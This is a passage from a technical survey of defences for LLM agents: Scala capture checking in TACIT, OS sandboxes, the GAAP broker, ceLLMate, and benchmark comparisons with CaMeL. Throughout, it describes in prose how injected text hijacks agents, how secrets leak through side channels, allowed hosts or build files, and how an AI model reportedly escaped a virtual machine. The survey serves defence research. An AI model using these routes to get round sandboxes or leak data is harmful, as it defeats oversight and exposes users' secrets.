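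Mettler and colleagues see taming as a substantial weakness, because one wrong decision can break the guarantee. Reviewers of a browser written in E found that E's taming list allowed several methods it should have blocked.

If code can gain access only from code that already has it, some code must receive the first capability. According to *Vx* (2026), the languages Pony and Austral give it to the function that starts the program. Vx, a new language, does the same, but its trusted code can still call the operating system directly. An audit option lists the code that does.

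### Capture sets

Limiting what a program can reach is not enough when its task requires both a secret and a way to send it. If an agent must summarise a confidential contract and also write public notes, a reviewer would want to know that the part of the agent handling the contract cannot reach the public file.

Joe-E can guarantee limits on what a whole plugin can do. In one example, an application downloads an image decoder from an untrusted source. The application requires the decoder to be immutable and to exchange only byte arrays, and Joe-E's verifier checks this before the program runs. A malicious decoder can then produce a wrong picture, but it cannot write a file, send network packets or retain data from one image while decoding the next.

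Scala 3 has an experimental feature, capture checking, that gives such guarantees for single functions. It adds to each type a capture set, the list of capabilities that a value of that type may reach. If `out` is an open file and `log` is a logger that writes to it, the types look like this:

```scala
String                 // pure: reaches no capability
Logger^{out}           // a logger that may reach out
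Logger^                // a logger that may reach any capability

String -> Int          // a pure function
String ->{log} Int     // a function that may use log and nothing else
String => Int          // a function that may use anything
```

The compiler works out most of these sets itself. A function that calls `log` gets `log` in its set, and the type of `log` shows that it can reach `out`. *Scoped Capabilities for Polymorphic Effects* (2022) gives the less obvious example of a lazy list, which computes its elements only when the program uses them. If computing an element writes to a log, the list's type must include the logger, because the list will use it later.

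A value with a smaller capture set can stand in for one with a larger set, but not the other way round. If `<:` means "can stand in for", then:

```
A  <:  A^{log}  <:  A^{log, out}  <:  A^
```

A function's set may include capabilities it never uses. For example, a function that uses `log` only in a branch that never runs still has `log` in its set. This causes some harmless programs to be rejected, but the sets also include effects in skipped branches, whereas CaMeL's labels could miss a flow when a branch is skipped.

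The capture checker runs after the ordinary type checker. *What's in the Box* (2025) reports that capture checking took less than 15% of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

### Access that ends with its block

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, by Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, uses capture checking in TACIT, a server that lets an agent run Scala code. The agent can be an existing product such as Claude Code. The Scala compiler checks each snippet the model writes, and accepted snippets access files, run commands and use the network through TACIT's library.

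To use files, the code asks for a directory and supplies a block:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  access("README.md").read()
}
```

The library creates a capability for the directory, makes it available inside the block, and withdraws it when the block ends. A model could try to keep the access by returning a function that uses it:

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/project") {
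  () => access("README.md").read()
}
later()
```

The capture set of the returned function would have to include the file capability. That capability exists only inside the block, so the type of the block's result cannot refer to it, and the compiler rejects the snippet. In one test run, a model's code returned a list of open files, and the compiler rejected it for the same reason.

Like ELBA's `//` operator, the library checks each path at run time and refuses any outside the requested directory. Code requests commands and network hosts the same way, by listing the ones it may use inside the block.

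Classic capability systems forbid global capabilities, since any code could use them. Scala can allow them because each use appears in a type. A function that prints through the global object `Console.out` has `Console.out` in its capture set, so its type shows that it is not pure. Existing programs therefore need less restructuring than they would in E or Joe-E.

### The six restrictions of safe mode

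Capture sets are reliable only if code cannot remove a capability from a type. Full Scala allows this in several ways. Scala's *Safe Mode* describes a subset of the language for code from agents and other untrusted sources, with six restrictions:

1. Code may not use unchecked type casts or pattern matches.
2. It may not use the module `caps.unsafe`, which lets trusted code avoid tracking.
3. It may not use `@unchecked` annotations, which turn off checks by the compiler.
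4. It may not use reflection at run time.
5. It must compile with capture checking on, including tracking of changes to data.
6. It may use global objects only if they are themselves safe.

Casts, the unsafe module, the annotations and reflection could each stop the compiler from tracking a capability. Full tracking ensures that a function with a pure type is pure, and the rule on global objects prevents library calls from adding effects that don't appear in any type.

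That last rule requires a list of safe library code, so Scala has the same taming problem as Joe-E. The list is part of the compiler and includes most of Scala's own library, but not the global print functions. A library author can add code to the list with the annotation `@assumeSafe`, which agent code cannot use. Like Haskell's Trustworthy mark, the annotation is a promise that the compiler does not check.

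One of Scala's examples would suit the email to Bob. The ordinary mailer is not on the safe list, so agent code cannot call it. A small `CheckedMailer`, marked `@assumeSafe`, shows each message to the user and passes it to the ordinary mailer only if the user agrees. `CheckedMailer` is a guard library, but the compiler stops agent code from bypassing it.

### The Classified wrapper

TACIT's administrator can declare some files secret. The library returns their contents in a wrapper, which in simplified form is:

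```scala
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The `map` method applies a function to the hidden contents and wraps the result. The thin arrow means that the function must be pure. Here are two attempts to use it:

```scala
val contract = readClassified("secrets/contract.txt")
val copy     = access("public/copy.txt")

contract.map(text => text.length)          // accepted
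contract.map(text => copy.write(text))     // rejected
```

The function in the last line uses the file `copy`, so the compiler gives it the type `String ->{copy} Unit`, where `Unit` means it returns nothing useful. The `map` method requires a function with an empty capture set, but this function's capture set contains `copy`, so the compiler reports that `copy` cannot flow into the empty set. The whole snippet fails to compile, so none of it runs.

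A model could instead try to open the public file inside the function. That also fails, because `requestFileSystem` needs an I/O capability, which would then appear in the function's capture set.

Pure functions can count, search and reformat text, but they cannot summarise a contract. For that, TACIT offers the function `chat`, which sends wrapped text to a second model that the user trusts, perhaps one on the user's own machine, and wraps the answer. This is the dual-LLM pattern, but it uses a type instead of a controller. The type system treats `chat` as pure even though it contacts another program, so whoever runs TACIT has to make sure that the second model has no tools and keeps no memory of earlier requests.

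### What the user and the model see

The user usually wants to read the summary, but the model that wrote the code must not see it. TACIT therefore has two output channels. Ordinary values go to both. When a program prints a wrapped value, the user's channel shows the real text and the model receives only `Classified(****)`.

The summary stays wrapped across requests, although the file access from the first request has ended. If the user next asks how long the summary is, the model can write `summary.map(_.length)` and print the result. The user sees the number, and the model again receives asterisks.

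Exceptions could leak information to the model. For example, a function might fail only if a contract mentions a certain company. Scala does not track exceptions in types, since almost any operation can fail, so TACIT catches them and hides their messages from the model. This makes debugging harder. The instructions for one set of tests include a warning that a failed function looks like a success to the model, while the user gets an empty result.

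### The leak benchmark

Odersky and colleagues tested the wrapper on a sample Scala project with a directory of secrets, including API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary tasks, such as listing what a program offers or summarising a secret incident report. They paired each task with 10 injections, giving 120 trials. Some injections were simple notes in code comments. Others imitated a tool error that required a password, claimed that the secrets were only test data, or included ready-to-run Scala code.

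Another 11 trials had no injection, because the request itself was malicious. Five asked directly for secrets, and six used a pretext such as an administrator's emergency. Two models did all 131 trials with the wrapper and again with the secrets as plain text. The scores are the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

| Model | Trials | With wrapper | Without wrapper |
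|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100% | 100% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

The injections were a weak test, because without the wrapper they caused only 3 leaks in 240 trials. The other 10 leaks came from the malicious requests. The perfect scores show that the wrapper worked as designed with two quite different models, but this was expected, since the model never receives the secret text. Odersky and colleagues describe no attacks that try to exploit a compiler bug, which would be more dangerous.

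The score also counts only the agent's output. Someone who makes a malicious request and can read the user's channel would still see the secrets there. The wrapper hides data from the model and the company that runs it, so an administrator who distrusts the users has to control that channel separately.

The wrapper did not reduce the number of completed tasks. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the injection trials with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's lower score without the wrapper is partly an artefact, because Sonnet often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

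### The case against run-time tracking

Odersky and colleagues compare TACIT with CaMeL and argue for checking code in advance over labelling data at run time. LLMbda is a useful test of their arguments because it tracks labels at run time without some of CaMeL's limits.

The most convincing argument for TACIT is local purity, the ability to require that one part of a program has no side effects. Neither CaMeL nor LLMbda can express this. LLMbda checks labels when the code reaches a tool, so it may stop a program halfway, after earlier actions have taken effect, while TACIT rejects the program before it starts.

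However, purity stops a function inside `map` from emailing a document to anyone, even to Bob when he is allowed to read it. CaMeL's labels list the permitted readers, so its policy can allow an email to Bob and block one to the attacker. In TACIT, the developer has to write a separate library function for each kind of disclosure they want to allow.

Odersky and colleagues also object that CaMeL bans user-defined and recursive functions, both of which TACIT allows. They argue that lifting the ban while still providing guarantees before the program runs would require an analysis that can take exponential time. This objection applies to predicting flows without help from types, but not to labels that an interpreter attaches at run time, since LLMbda uses such labels and allows recursive functions.

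Their remaining argument is that labels disappear once a value enters the model's conversation. This is true of CaMeL but not of LLMbda, where Garby and colleagues label the conversation itself. Labeling the conversation leads to label creep, which TACIT avoids for secrets because they never enter the conversation.

Keeping secrets out of the prompt also protects them from the company that runs the model. TACIT provides this protection by default, while in LLMbda and ELBA the developer would have to add a check on what goes into each prompt.

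### Secrecy without integrity

LLMbda protects better than TACIT against untrusted text. Suppose the meeting notes are an ordinary file. TACIT returns them as plain text, and the model reads the attacker's line along with the rest. Its next snippet may then send Bob's document to the attacker if the agent has a mail capability and the document is not wrapped. That snippet type-checks. Odersky and colleagues promise only that such text cannot make the agent exceed its capabilities, and sending email is within them. LLMbda would have marked the conversation as untrusted, so a mail tool that requires a trusted address would not send the document.

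If the notes are classified instead, the model never reads the planted line. The trusted model can extract an address, but the result is a `Classified[String]`. A mail function that expects an ordinary string will not accept it, and `map` does not let the program send email from inside the wrapper. The program therefore cannot send the document to anyone, including Bob. The developer could add a mail function that accepts a wrapped address and checks whether its owner may read the document, which would reimplement CaMeL's policy in a trusted library.

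Enforcement then depends on the library declaring its effects correctly. In TACIT's version of AgentDojo, functions such as `sendEmail` do not require a capability. The model's instructions include a warning that side effects inside `map` happen immediately, which suggests that the compiler accepts them there. If so, a program can send email to an address it has read inside the wrapper, and the main protection comes from keeping attackers' text away from the model that writes the code.

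Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's documentation, states that the wrapper "protects confidentiality, not integrity". Agent code can wrap any text and write it to a secret file, so it could, for instance, replace the list of keys that allow people to log in to a machine. An administrator can prevent this by making secret files read-only.

### What the guarantee leaves out

Like ELBA, TACIT has a large compiler in its trusted base, along with the runtime and the library. Every function marked `@assumeSafe` adds to that base. Scala's example is a cache that stores earlier results in an untracked variable. The cache is harmless only if it always returns what the original function would, and a person has to verify that.

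*Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proves type safety for an extended form of capture checking, with every step checked in Lean. But Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that showing safe mode delivers the promised purity still requires a separate argument.

The software is also young. Scala's documentation calls capture checking "still highly experimental and unstable". According to lampepfl's *TACIT*, the documentation in the project's repository, TACIT did not yet use the compiler's safe mode in March 2026. It instead searched each snippet for forbidden patterns, which has the same weakness as matching shell commands. By October TACIT could also turn on safe mode. The documentation's list of options gives safe mode as the default, but another passage still gives the pattern search. Scala Days' *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* announced that EPFL, the Swiss university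 where TACIT began, is building a production-grade agent on it with the software company VirtusLab.

Whether TACIT mediates all of an agent's actions depends on how the user sets up the agent. A coding agent usually has its own tools for files, shell commands and web pages, and calls to those tools bypass TACIT. The documentation therefore advises users to turn the tools off. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala* warns against classifying too much data, since an agent that cannot read or change the user's data is of little use.

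Secrets can still leak through side channels. For example, a function inside `map` may take longer if a secret contains a certain digit, so its running time reveals something about the secret. Odersky and colleagues treat such leaks as out of scope and describe them as revealing a single bit, but a hostile model can repeat the attack. A key of 40 hexadecimal digits contains 160 bits, so 160 runs that leak one bit each could reveal it. If the administrator has set a time limit, the model doesn't even need a clock, because TACIT reports an error when a snippet exceeds the limit.

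Code can also send wrapped data over the network to any host on the permitted list. This lets an agent log in to a service with a password it cannot read, for example. But if the list includes a site where anyone can open an account, injected code might send the data to the attacker's account there.

External commands are the largest gap, because Scala's types do not apply to the programs they start. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific safe commands and give `git diff` and `sbt` as examples. But `sbt`, Scala's build tool, runs whatever code the project's build file contains. An agent that can edit that file can make `sbt` read a secret and print it as ordinary text. For security-critical deployments, Odersky and colleagues advise running TACIT inside a sandbox, which also restricts the programs the agent starts.

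## Sandboxes outside the language

A sandbox can limit `sbt` and the other programs that TACIT's types do not cover, because it restricts the running process rather than the code. A Python or Haskell program, a shell script and a compiled program from the internet must all go through the operating system to open a file or a network connection, and a sandbox controls those requests.

### What each kind intercepts

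A program asks the kernel, the core of the operating system, for files and connections through system calls. Sandboxes differ in what they intercept and in which software has to be correct:

| Kind of sandbox | What it intercepts | What it trusts |
|---|---|---|
| System-call and file restrictions (seccomp, Landlock, bubblewrap) | The process's requests to the host's kernel | The host's kernel |
| Container | The same requests | The host's kernel and the container software |
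| User-space kernel (gVisor) | System calls, which a second kernel answers | The second kernel and the parts of the host's kernel that it uses |
| Small virtual machine (Firecracker) | The guest system's use of virtual hardware | The processor, the virtual machine software and the host's kernel |
| JavaScript isolate | Calls to functions that the application supplies | The JavaScript engine and those functions |
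| WebAssembly | Calls to functions that the application supplies | The WebAssembly runtime and those functions |

Seccomp, one of several Linux restrictions that a sandbox can combine, filters system calls by their number and arguments. Kerrisk (2023) lists Docker and Chrome among its users. A seccomp filter can detect that a program is trying to open a file, but not which file, because the file's name reaches the kernel as a pointer into the program's memory and filters cannot follow pointers. If they could, the program might change the name after the check but before the kernel used it. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *Seccomp BPF (SECure COMPuting with filters)*, system call filtering "isn't a sandbox" but a tool for sandbox developers.

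With Landlock, a process lists the directories it still needs and gives up access to the rest. Any program it starts inherits these limits. The process needs no administrator rights to restrict itself this way (Salaün, *Landlock*, 2026). Bubblewrap instead starts a program in namespaces, which are separate views of the system's files, processes and network. A program in an empty network namespace cannot reach the internet, whichever library it uses.

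Containers package an application with its own files and use the same kernel features to isolate it. They share the host's kernel, as Pillar Security points out, so one kernel bug may let a program escape from any of them. gVisor reduces this risk by running a second kernel as an ordinary program, which handles most system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the host. Firecracker runs each workload in a virtual machine with its own full Linux kernel. It emulates very few devices, which reduces the amount of host code exposed to attack.

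JavaScript isolates and WebAssembly modules work more like Monty. An isolate has its own memory and global objects inside a JavaScript engine, and its script has no file or network functions unless the application adds them. WebAssembly is an instruction format that compilers can produce from languages such as C and Rust. A module can address only its own memory and call only the outside functions that the application gives it. Neither can run an ordinary shell command, so they suit agents that write self-contained code better than agents that use a developer's existing tools.

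### How coding agents combine file and network limits

Coding agents need those existing tools, so they usually rely on operating system restrictions. The documentation from Anthropic, OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* and Cursor's *Terminal* describes similar designs with different defaults. On Linux they compare as follows:

| | Claude Code | Codex | Cursor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sandbox on by default | No | Yes | Yes |
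| Mechanism | Bubblewrap, with an optional seccomp filter | Bubblewrap and seccomp | Landlock, with bubblewrap as a fallback |
| Where commands can write | Working directory and a temporary directory | Workspace and temporary directories | Workspace and temporary directories |
| Default network access | Hosts that the user approves | None | The user's list plus a built-in list of development sites |

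File limits and network limits depend on each other. Anthropic explains that a hijacked agent could send out the user's login keys if there were no network limits, and could alter the system to regain network access if there were no file limits. By default, commands in Claude Code's sandbox can read almost the whole computer, including files that hold passwords and keys. Unless the user blocks those files, only the network limits prevent a hijacked agent from sending out their contents.

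Some files stay read-only even inside the working directory, because a command that could edit Claude Code's settings might grant itself permissions or add a program that Claude Code later runs outside the sandbox. Codex protects its own configuration directory and `.git` for the same reason that Anderson required a tamper-proof monitor.

Claude Code controls network access on Linux in four steps:

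1. The command starts in a network namespace with no connection to the outside.
2. Environment variables direct it to a proxy that runs outside the sandbox.
3. The proxy compares the requested host's name with the lists of allowed and denied hosts. If the host is on neither list, Claude Code can ask the user.
4. If the answer is yes, the proxy relays the connection, normally without decrypting it.

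A program that ignores the environment variables gets no connection. Most database drivers ignore them, so they fail even when their host is on the list. This is inconvenient, but it also stops programs from getting around the check by opening their own connections. The Python code that bypassed a guard library by connecting to `attacker.example` would fail here.

### Bob's email through an allowed host

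Suppose the agent sends email through a provider at `mail.example`, which the developer has put on the allowlist. Whether the message goes to Bob or to the attacker, the proxy receives this:

```
host:      mail.example, port 443
contents:  encrypted
```

The recipient's address is in the encrypted part. The sandbox can block both emails or neither.

Hostile code can also misuse an allowed service. Cursor's built-in list includes `github.com` and `*.googleapis.com`. Anyone can open a GitHub account, and Google's interfaces for email and file storage match the second entry, so injected code could upload a document to the attacker's account. Anthropic warns about broad entries such as `github.com` and about domain fronting, in which a program gives the proxy an allowed host's name but names another host inside the encrypted request. Some shared hosting networks forward the request to the second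 host.

### A proxy that reads the request

A proxy can identify an email's recipient if it decrypts the traffic. In *httpjail*, Willison (2025) describes an experimental tool that isolates a process from the network and sends its web requests through a proxy. The proxy's rules are JavaScript expressions or custom programs, so a rule could compare the recipient with a contact list. The developer has to make the sandboxed programs accept the proxy's certificate so that it can read encrypted requests, and someone has to write rules that parse each service's message format.

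The proxy can also keep credentials out of the sandbox. In an optional Claude Code setup, a command receives a placeholder instead of the user's GitHub token, and the proxy substitutes the real token in requests to permitted hosts. Injected code can still use the token through the proxy, but it cannot copy it and use it later from somewhere else.

### GAAP: which data may go to whom

*An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) describes GAAP, a system that places a broker between the agent and its tool servers. Each stored permission pairs one item of private data with one outside party, such as "date of birth" with an airline. If no permission covers a proposed tool call, GAAP pauses the agent, asks the user, and saves the answer for next time.

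GAAP must determine who receives the data in each call. An email provider's server is a single network destination but can deliver to anyone, so a short annotation on each tool identifies the outside recipient, which for email is the value of the `to` argument. Stanley and colleagues say that writing the annotations takes minutes per server, and they expect an open-source community to share and check them.

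The broker also has to identify the data in a message, which it cannot do from the text alone. GAAP therefore makes the model write its plan in a small language with only two kinds of instruction, tool calls and conditional jumps. An interpreter runs the plan and labels each result with the private data it was derived from. At a conditional jump, it labels the instructions on every path until the paths meet again, including instructions that do not run. This should avoid the leak through skipped branches that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL.

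For Bob's email, GAAP would first check that the user allows the quarantined model to read the notes. Before sending the document, it would check for permission to send it to the address from the notes. If it found none, it would ask the user something like "Should the contents of Q3 forecast be sent to bob@attacker.example?" The user would have to notice the wrong address, even though the first request about Bob's real address looks much the same. But once the user has approved the real address for that document, repeating the task raises no question, so an unexpected question about the same document is a sign that the address has changed.

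GAAP also keeps a log of everything it has disclosed. In one example, the agent gives an airline the user's passport number to check in for a flight. Later the user asks it to forward the airline's confirmation to a friend. The second task doesn't mention a passport, but the log records that the airline received the number, so the confirmation may include it. GAAP therefore checks for permission to share the passport number with the friend. CaMeL's labels last for only one program, so they would not carry over to the second task.

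Stanley and colleagues do not assume that the model, the user's prompt or any data is free of attacks, but in exchange they promise only confidentiality. An injection could still make the agent delete a file, or send Bob the wrong document if the user has already approved sharing that document with him. GAAP also does not protect private data that the user types into the prompt, so the user should write "my date of birth" and let GAAP supply the date.

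In the researchers' tests, GAAP leaked nothing under seven injections on each of 20 tasks. Five of the seven succeeded on at least one task when a second model judged each tool call, and five also did against Conseca, which enforces policies written by an isolated model. The researchers built this test suite around GAAP's threat model, so it provides little evidence of how the other defences perform elsewhere. On AgentDojo, with every disclosure approved, GAAP completed about as many tasks as an unprotected agent. On AgentDyn it did 10% worse, partly because later results made instructions in its plans unsuitable.

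Saved permissions reduced the number of questions from 3.8 to 1.5 per task in a separate run of 100 tasks. That run included many variations of the same tasks, which favours saved answers. Planning was slow, averaging 188 seconds per task on the two public benchmarks, compared with 28 for the unprotected agent.

GAAP works because personal assistants use tools with defined arguments. Coding agents often write a new shell script for each job, and Stanley and colleagues note that it is harder to analyse how such a script interacts with outside services. An ordinary sandbox can confine the script, but GAAP cannot use its labels to track data through it.

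### ceLLMate: from clicks to web requests

Agents that operate a browser have a different visibility problem, because they act by clicking and typing, and a click at a given position may open an email or delete it. In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) stopped an agent from opening Hacker News directly, but it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

Their system, ceLLMate, ignores clicks and checks the web requests they cause. Each website publishes an "agent sitemap", which translates requests into named actions. A simplified version might contain:

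```
POST gitlab.com/-/user_settings/ssh_keys         AddSSHKey
GET  amazon.com/gp/cart/view.html                ViewCart
POST amazon.com/checkout/p/*/spc/place-order     PlaceOrder
```

Policies use these names. The website or an administrator prepares a list of policies, a language model selects the ones the user's request needs, and the user confirms the selection. The browser extension then blocks other actions, however the agent reaches them. An attacker may still trick the agent into clicking a fake cookie notice, but the extension blocks any forbidden request that results.

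Some rules depend on information that the request does not contain. To enforce a $50 limit on an Amazon order, ceLLMate reads the total from the checkout page and stores it until the agent places the order. A $50 limit per order would still permit two orders of $49, so a policy can also count requests.

Meng and colleagues tested ceLLMate's enforcement with 12 scripts that imitated a completely hijacked agent. The user's task was to comment on or upvote an issue in GitLab, a site for software projects. The scripts tried actions such as deleting a project or adding an attacker's login key, and ceLLMate blocked all 12. Every script needed a forbidden action, so the test did not cover misuse of permitted ones. An agent allowed to comment on an issue can put a secret in the comment, because ceLLMate does not check the comment's contents.

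If Bob's email went through a webmail page, a sitemap could identify the request that sends a message and extract its recipient, which a policy could then compare with the user's contacts. ceLLMate would have about as much information as a guard library around `send_email`, but no record that the address came from the notes. It also depends on websites to write complete sitemaps and keep them current, and it doesn't cover WebSockets, which many sites use for live updates. ceLLMate slowed a series of page visits modestly, by between 7.25% and 15%, depending on the size of the sitemap.

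### Coverage of any program

Operating system sandboxes are most effective in the cases that language-level designs handle poorly. A sandbox that hides `secret.txt` stops every command that could evade a text pattern, because each has to go through the kernel to read the file. The developer does not need to know which language the agent will use or which packages it will install.

This coverage extends only to processes inside the sandbox. Claude Code runs shell commands in a sandbox, but its built-in file tools, external tool servers and the user's own hooks run outside it. Anthropic therefore considers that sandbox insufficient for fully unattended work and recommends running all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or a similar boundary.

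### Trusted base and configuration

This coverage relies on a very large trusted base. Linux has tens of millions of lines of code, far more than the operating system that Anderson judged too large to analyse. If the kernel counts as part of the check, Li and colleagues' favourable verdict on host sandboxes is therefore hard to accept. Zed, which makes a code editor with its own agent sandbox, tells users that both the operating system's features and Zed's use of them may contain bugs.

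A virtual machine has a narrower connection to the host than a container does, but it also relies on complex software. Dinaburg (2026) reported in *VMs won't contain cyber-capable agents* that a capable AI model had escaped from an ordinary virtual machine.

A sandbox without bugs can still fail because of its settings. NCC Group found that some coding agents leave sandboxing off by default and that implementations differ between operating systems. The documentation for Claude Code and Codex contains several examples:

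- If a required component is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands without a sandbox. An administrator can make it refuse to start instead.
- In Codex, network access and the proxy that restricts it are separate settings. A user who turns on only the first gives commands unrestricted access to the internet.
- Access to Docker's control socket lets a sandboxed command start containers that can reach the host's files.
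- A user may exempt `docker compose` from Claude Code's sandbox because Docker does not work inside it. The agent can then write a Compose file and run it with the user's full access.

The sandbox does what its settings specify in each case, but the user may not realise how much access they allow.

### A language-level check inside a sandbox

Zhou and colleagues describe types and operating system sandboxes as complementary. A sandbox confines a process to fixed directories, while a program can narrow a `Path` during the task, but the sandbox covers commands that Haskell cannot check.

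An application could use three components to send Bob's email. A container holds the agent's code but no passwords, and its only network connection leads to a broker. An interpreter inside the container labels values and applies a policy like CaMeL's. The broker, outside the container, holds the password for the mail account and sends the messages.

Normally the interpreter blocks emails to anyone who isn't allowed to read the document. If hostile code escapes the interpreter through a bug, it still has no password and no direct route to the attacker, but it can ask the broker to send an email with any labels. The broker therefore needs a check that doesn't depend on those labels, such as a contact list. This check is less precise, but it still works after the interpreter has failed.

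Sandbox boundaries also have to separate programs that need different access. TACIT must be able to read secret files, but `sbt` must not. One sandbox around both gives them the same access, so the developer has to start `sbt` in a second, stricter sandbox that hides the secrets.

Putting one sandbox inside another can weaken the inner one. According to NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agents with AI Workbench*, bubblewrap runs in a reduced mode inside containers, while Cursor's sandbox needs host support that a container may not provide. Claude Code has a setting that lets its sandbox run inside a container without special privileges, but Anthropic warns that this setting considerably weakens security. It is suitable only if the container already provides the isolation users need.

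## Security and completed tasks in direct comparisons

Three research teams have compared a language-level system of their own with CaMeL on AgentDojo. They chose different suites and models, and only two of them ran CaMeL themselves:

| System compared with CaMeL | AgentDojo suites | Models | Source of CaMeL's scores |
|---|---|---|---|
| ELBA (types and labels in Haskell) | Slack | Claude Opus 4.7, Claude Opus 4.8, Claude Sonnet 5, GPT 5.4 | Runs by Zhou and colleagues |
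| TACIT (tracked capabilities in Scala) | All four | Gemini 2.5 Pro, o4-mini-high | CaMeL's own paper |
| Randori (an agent written in LLMbda) | Banking | GPT-5.2, MiMo-v2.5, and Qwen3.7-plus for Randori only | Runs by Garby and colleagues |

### ELBA and CaMeL on the Slack suite

Zhou and colleagues ran both systems on the Slack suite's 21 user tasks and 105 attack pairs, with policies on and off. With policies off, CaMeL still keeps untrusted data away from its planner but no longer checks data flows, and ELBA's programs use a Slack library with plain `IO`. The researchers tried three wordings of the attack, so the columns below for runs under attack cover 315 runs per model.

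| Model | Policies | ELBA, no attack (of 21) | CaMeL, no attack (of 21) | ELBA, attacked (of 315) | CaMeL, attacked (of 315) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | On | 10 | 5 | 153 | 69 |
| Opus 4.8 | On | 9 | 6 | 141 | 89 |
| GPT 5.4 | On | 10 | 5 | 148 | 74 |
| Sonnet 5 | On | 8 | 4 | 129 | 71 |
| Opus 4.7 | Off | 18 | 15 | 264 | 211 |
| Opus 4.8 | Off | 16 | 16 | 275 | 242 |
| GPT 5.4 | Off | 16 | 17 | 243 | 248 |
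| Sonnet 5 | Off | 14 | 13 | 235 | 169 |

ELBA completed almost twice as many tasks as CaMeL with policies on. With policies off, ELBA completed about 17% more under attack, but without attacks the two systems completed nearly the same number, 64 and 61 of 84 runs. Zhou and colleagues also tried CaMeL's normal mode, and every result was within 4% of the strict-mode result, so strict mode does not explain CaMeL's low scores.

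The results without attacks are imprecise because each of the 21 tasks is worth almost five percentage points. With policies off, all four 95% confidence intervals for ELBA's lead include zero. The interval is −8.4 to +35.9 points for Opus 4.7 and −24.0 to +14.5 for GPT 5.4. With policies on, the interval for Opus 4.8 also includes zero (−7.4 to +34.1), but the interval for GPT 5.4 does not (+2.9 to +41.8).

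The attacked runs give narrower intervals. Under the simplest wording with policies on, ELBA's lead was at least 7.9 points for every model. But these runs repeat the same 21 user tasks with different injections, so they provide less information than 105 separate tasks would. They are good evidence that ELBA does better on this suite under these policies, but weaker evidence that it does better on other work.

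The lead has also changed between versions of the study. Garby and colleagues cite an older version, in which ELBA was called TypeGuard and completed 8 of the 21 tasks with policies on, while CaMeL completed 7.

### TACIT and CaMeL on four suites

In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky and colleagues ran TACIT on all four suites and copied the results for CaMeL with the same two models from its paper:

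| Suite | Gemini 2.5 Pro: CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro: TACIT | o4-mini-high: CaMeL | o4-mini-high: TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

Odersky and colleagues call the results for TACIT and CaMeL comparable, but TACIT completed fewer tasks in six of the eight comparisons. With o4-mini-high, it was 28.5 points behind on Workspace and 21 behind on Slack. TACIT had a large lead only on Travel with Gemini, where CaMeL completed almost no tasks. On the other three suites with Gemini, CaMeL averaged 51.7% and TACIT 49.2%.

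The researchers describe these percentages as shares of user tasks, but TACIT's exact Banking score with Gemini is 56.94%, which matches 82 of 144 attack pairs and does not correspond to any whole number of the suite's 16 tasks. The table therefore seems to report utility under attack, and its results should not be compared with results measured without attacks in other papers.

Writing Scala probably doesn't explain why TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL. On τ²-bench, a benchmark of airline and retail customer service, three other models had completion rates 0.8 to 3.7 points higher when they wrote typed Scala than when they made ordinary tool calls. Differences in prompts and tool descriptions could explain part of the gap between TACIT and CaMeL, since different teams ran the two systems.

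Each system let through one attack in 1,926 runs. In the attack TACIT let through, the user asked for a booking at one hotel, and the attacker had added a recommendation for another hotel to its reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo counted the second hotel's name as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues' table doesn't include an unprotected agent, so it doesn't show how many of the other attacks the compiler stopped and how many the models ignored.

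### LLMbda's agent on the banking suite

Garby and colleagues repeated each of the banking suite's 16 user tasks and 144 attack pairs three times. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs did not finish, and its results under attack exclude those runs.

| System | Model | Tasks done, no attack (of 48) | Tasks done under attack | Attacks resisted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 | 65.0% | 430 of 432 |
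| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 | 63.4% | 432 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 | 59.5% | 432 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 | 60.2% | 432 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 | 56.2% | 432 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 32 | 71.1% | 239 of 240 |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 | 72.2% | 378 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 18 | 30.0% | 231 of 231 |
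| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 | 41.5% | 357 of 357 |

Although Randori always checks labels, Garby and colleagues found that it completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies off. They based that finding on wide confidence intervals, roughly 20 points either way for tasks without an attack. Under attack, CaMeL without policies completed more tasks than Randori with both models tested on the two systems, by almost 13 points with MiMo. Randori's advantage over CaMeL with policies on is clearer, particularly under attack.

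Randori resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks when endorsement was available. Both failures were GPT-5.2 runs of the same attack pair. In that pair, the attacker replaces the bill that the user wants to pay, and the planner has already endorsed the file's details. CaMeL's paper reports a successful attack of the same kind and treats it as outside its threat model.

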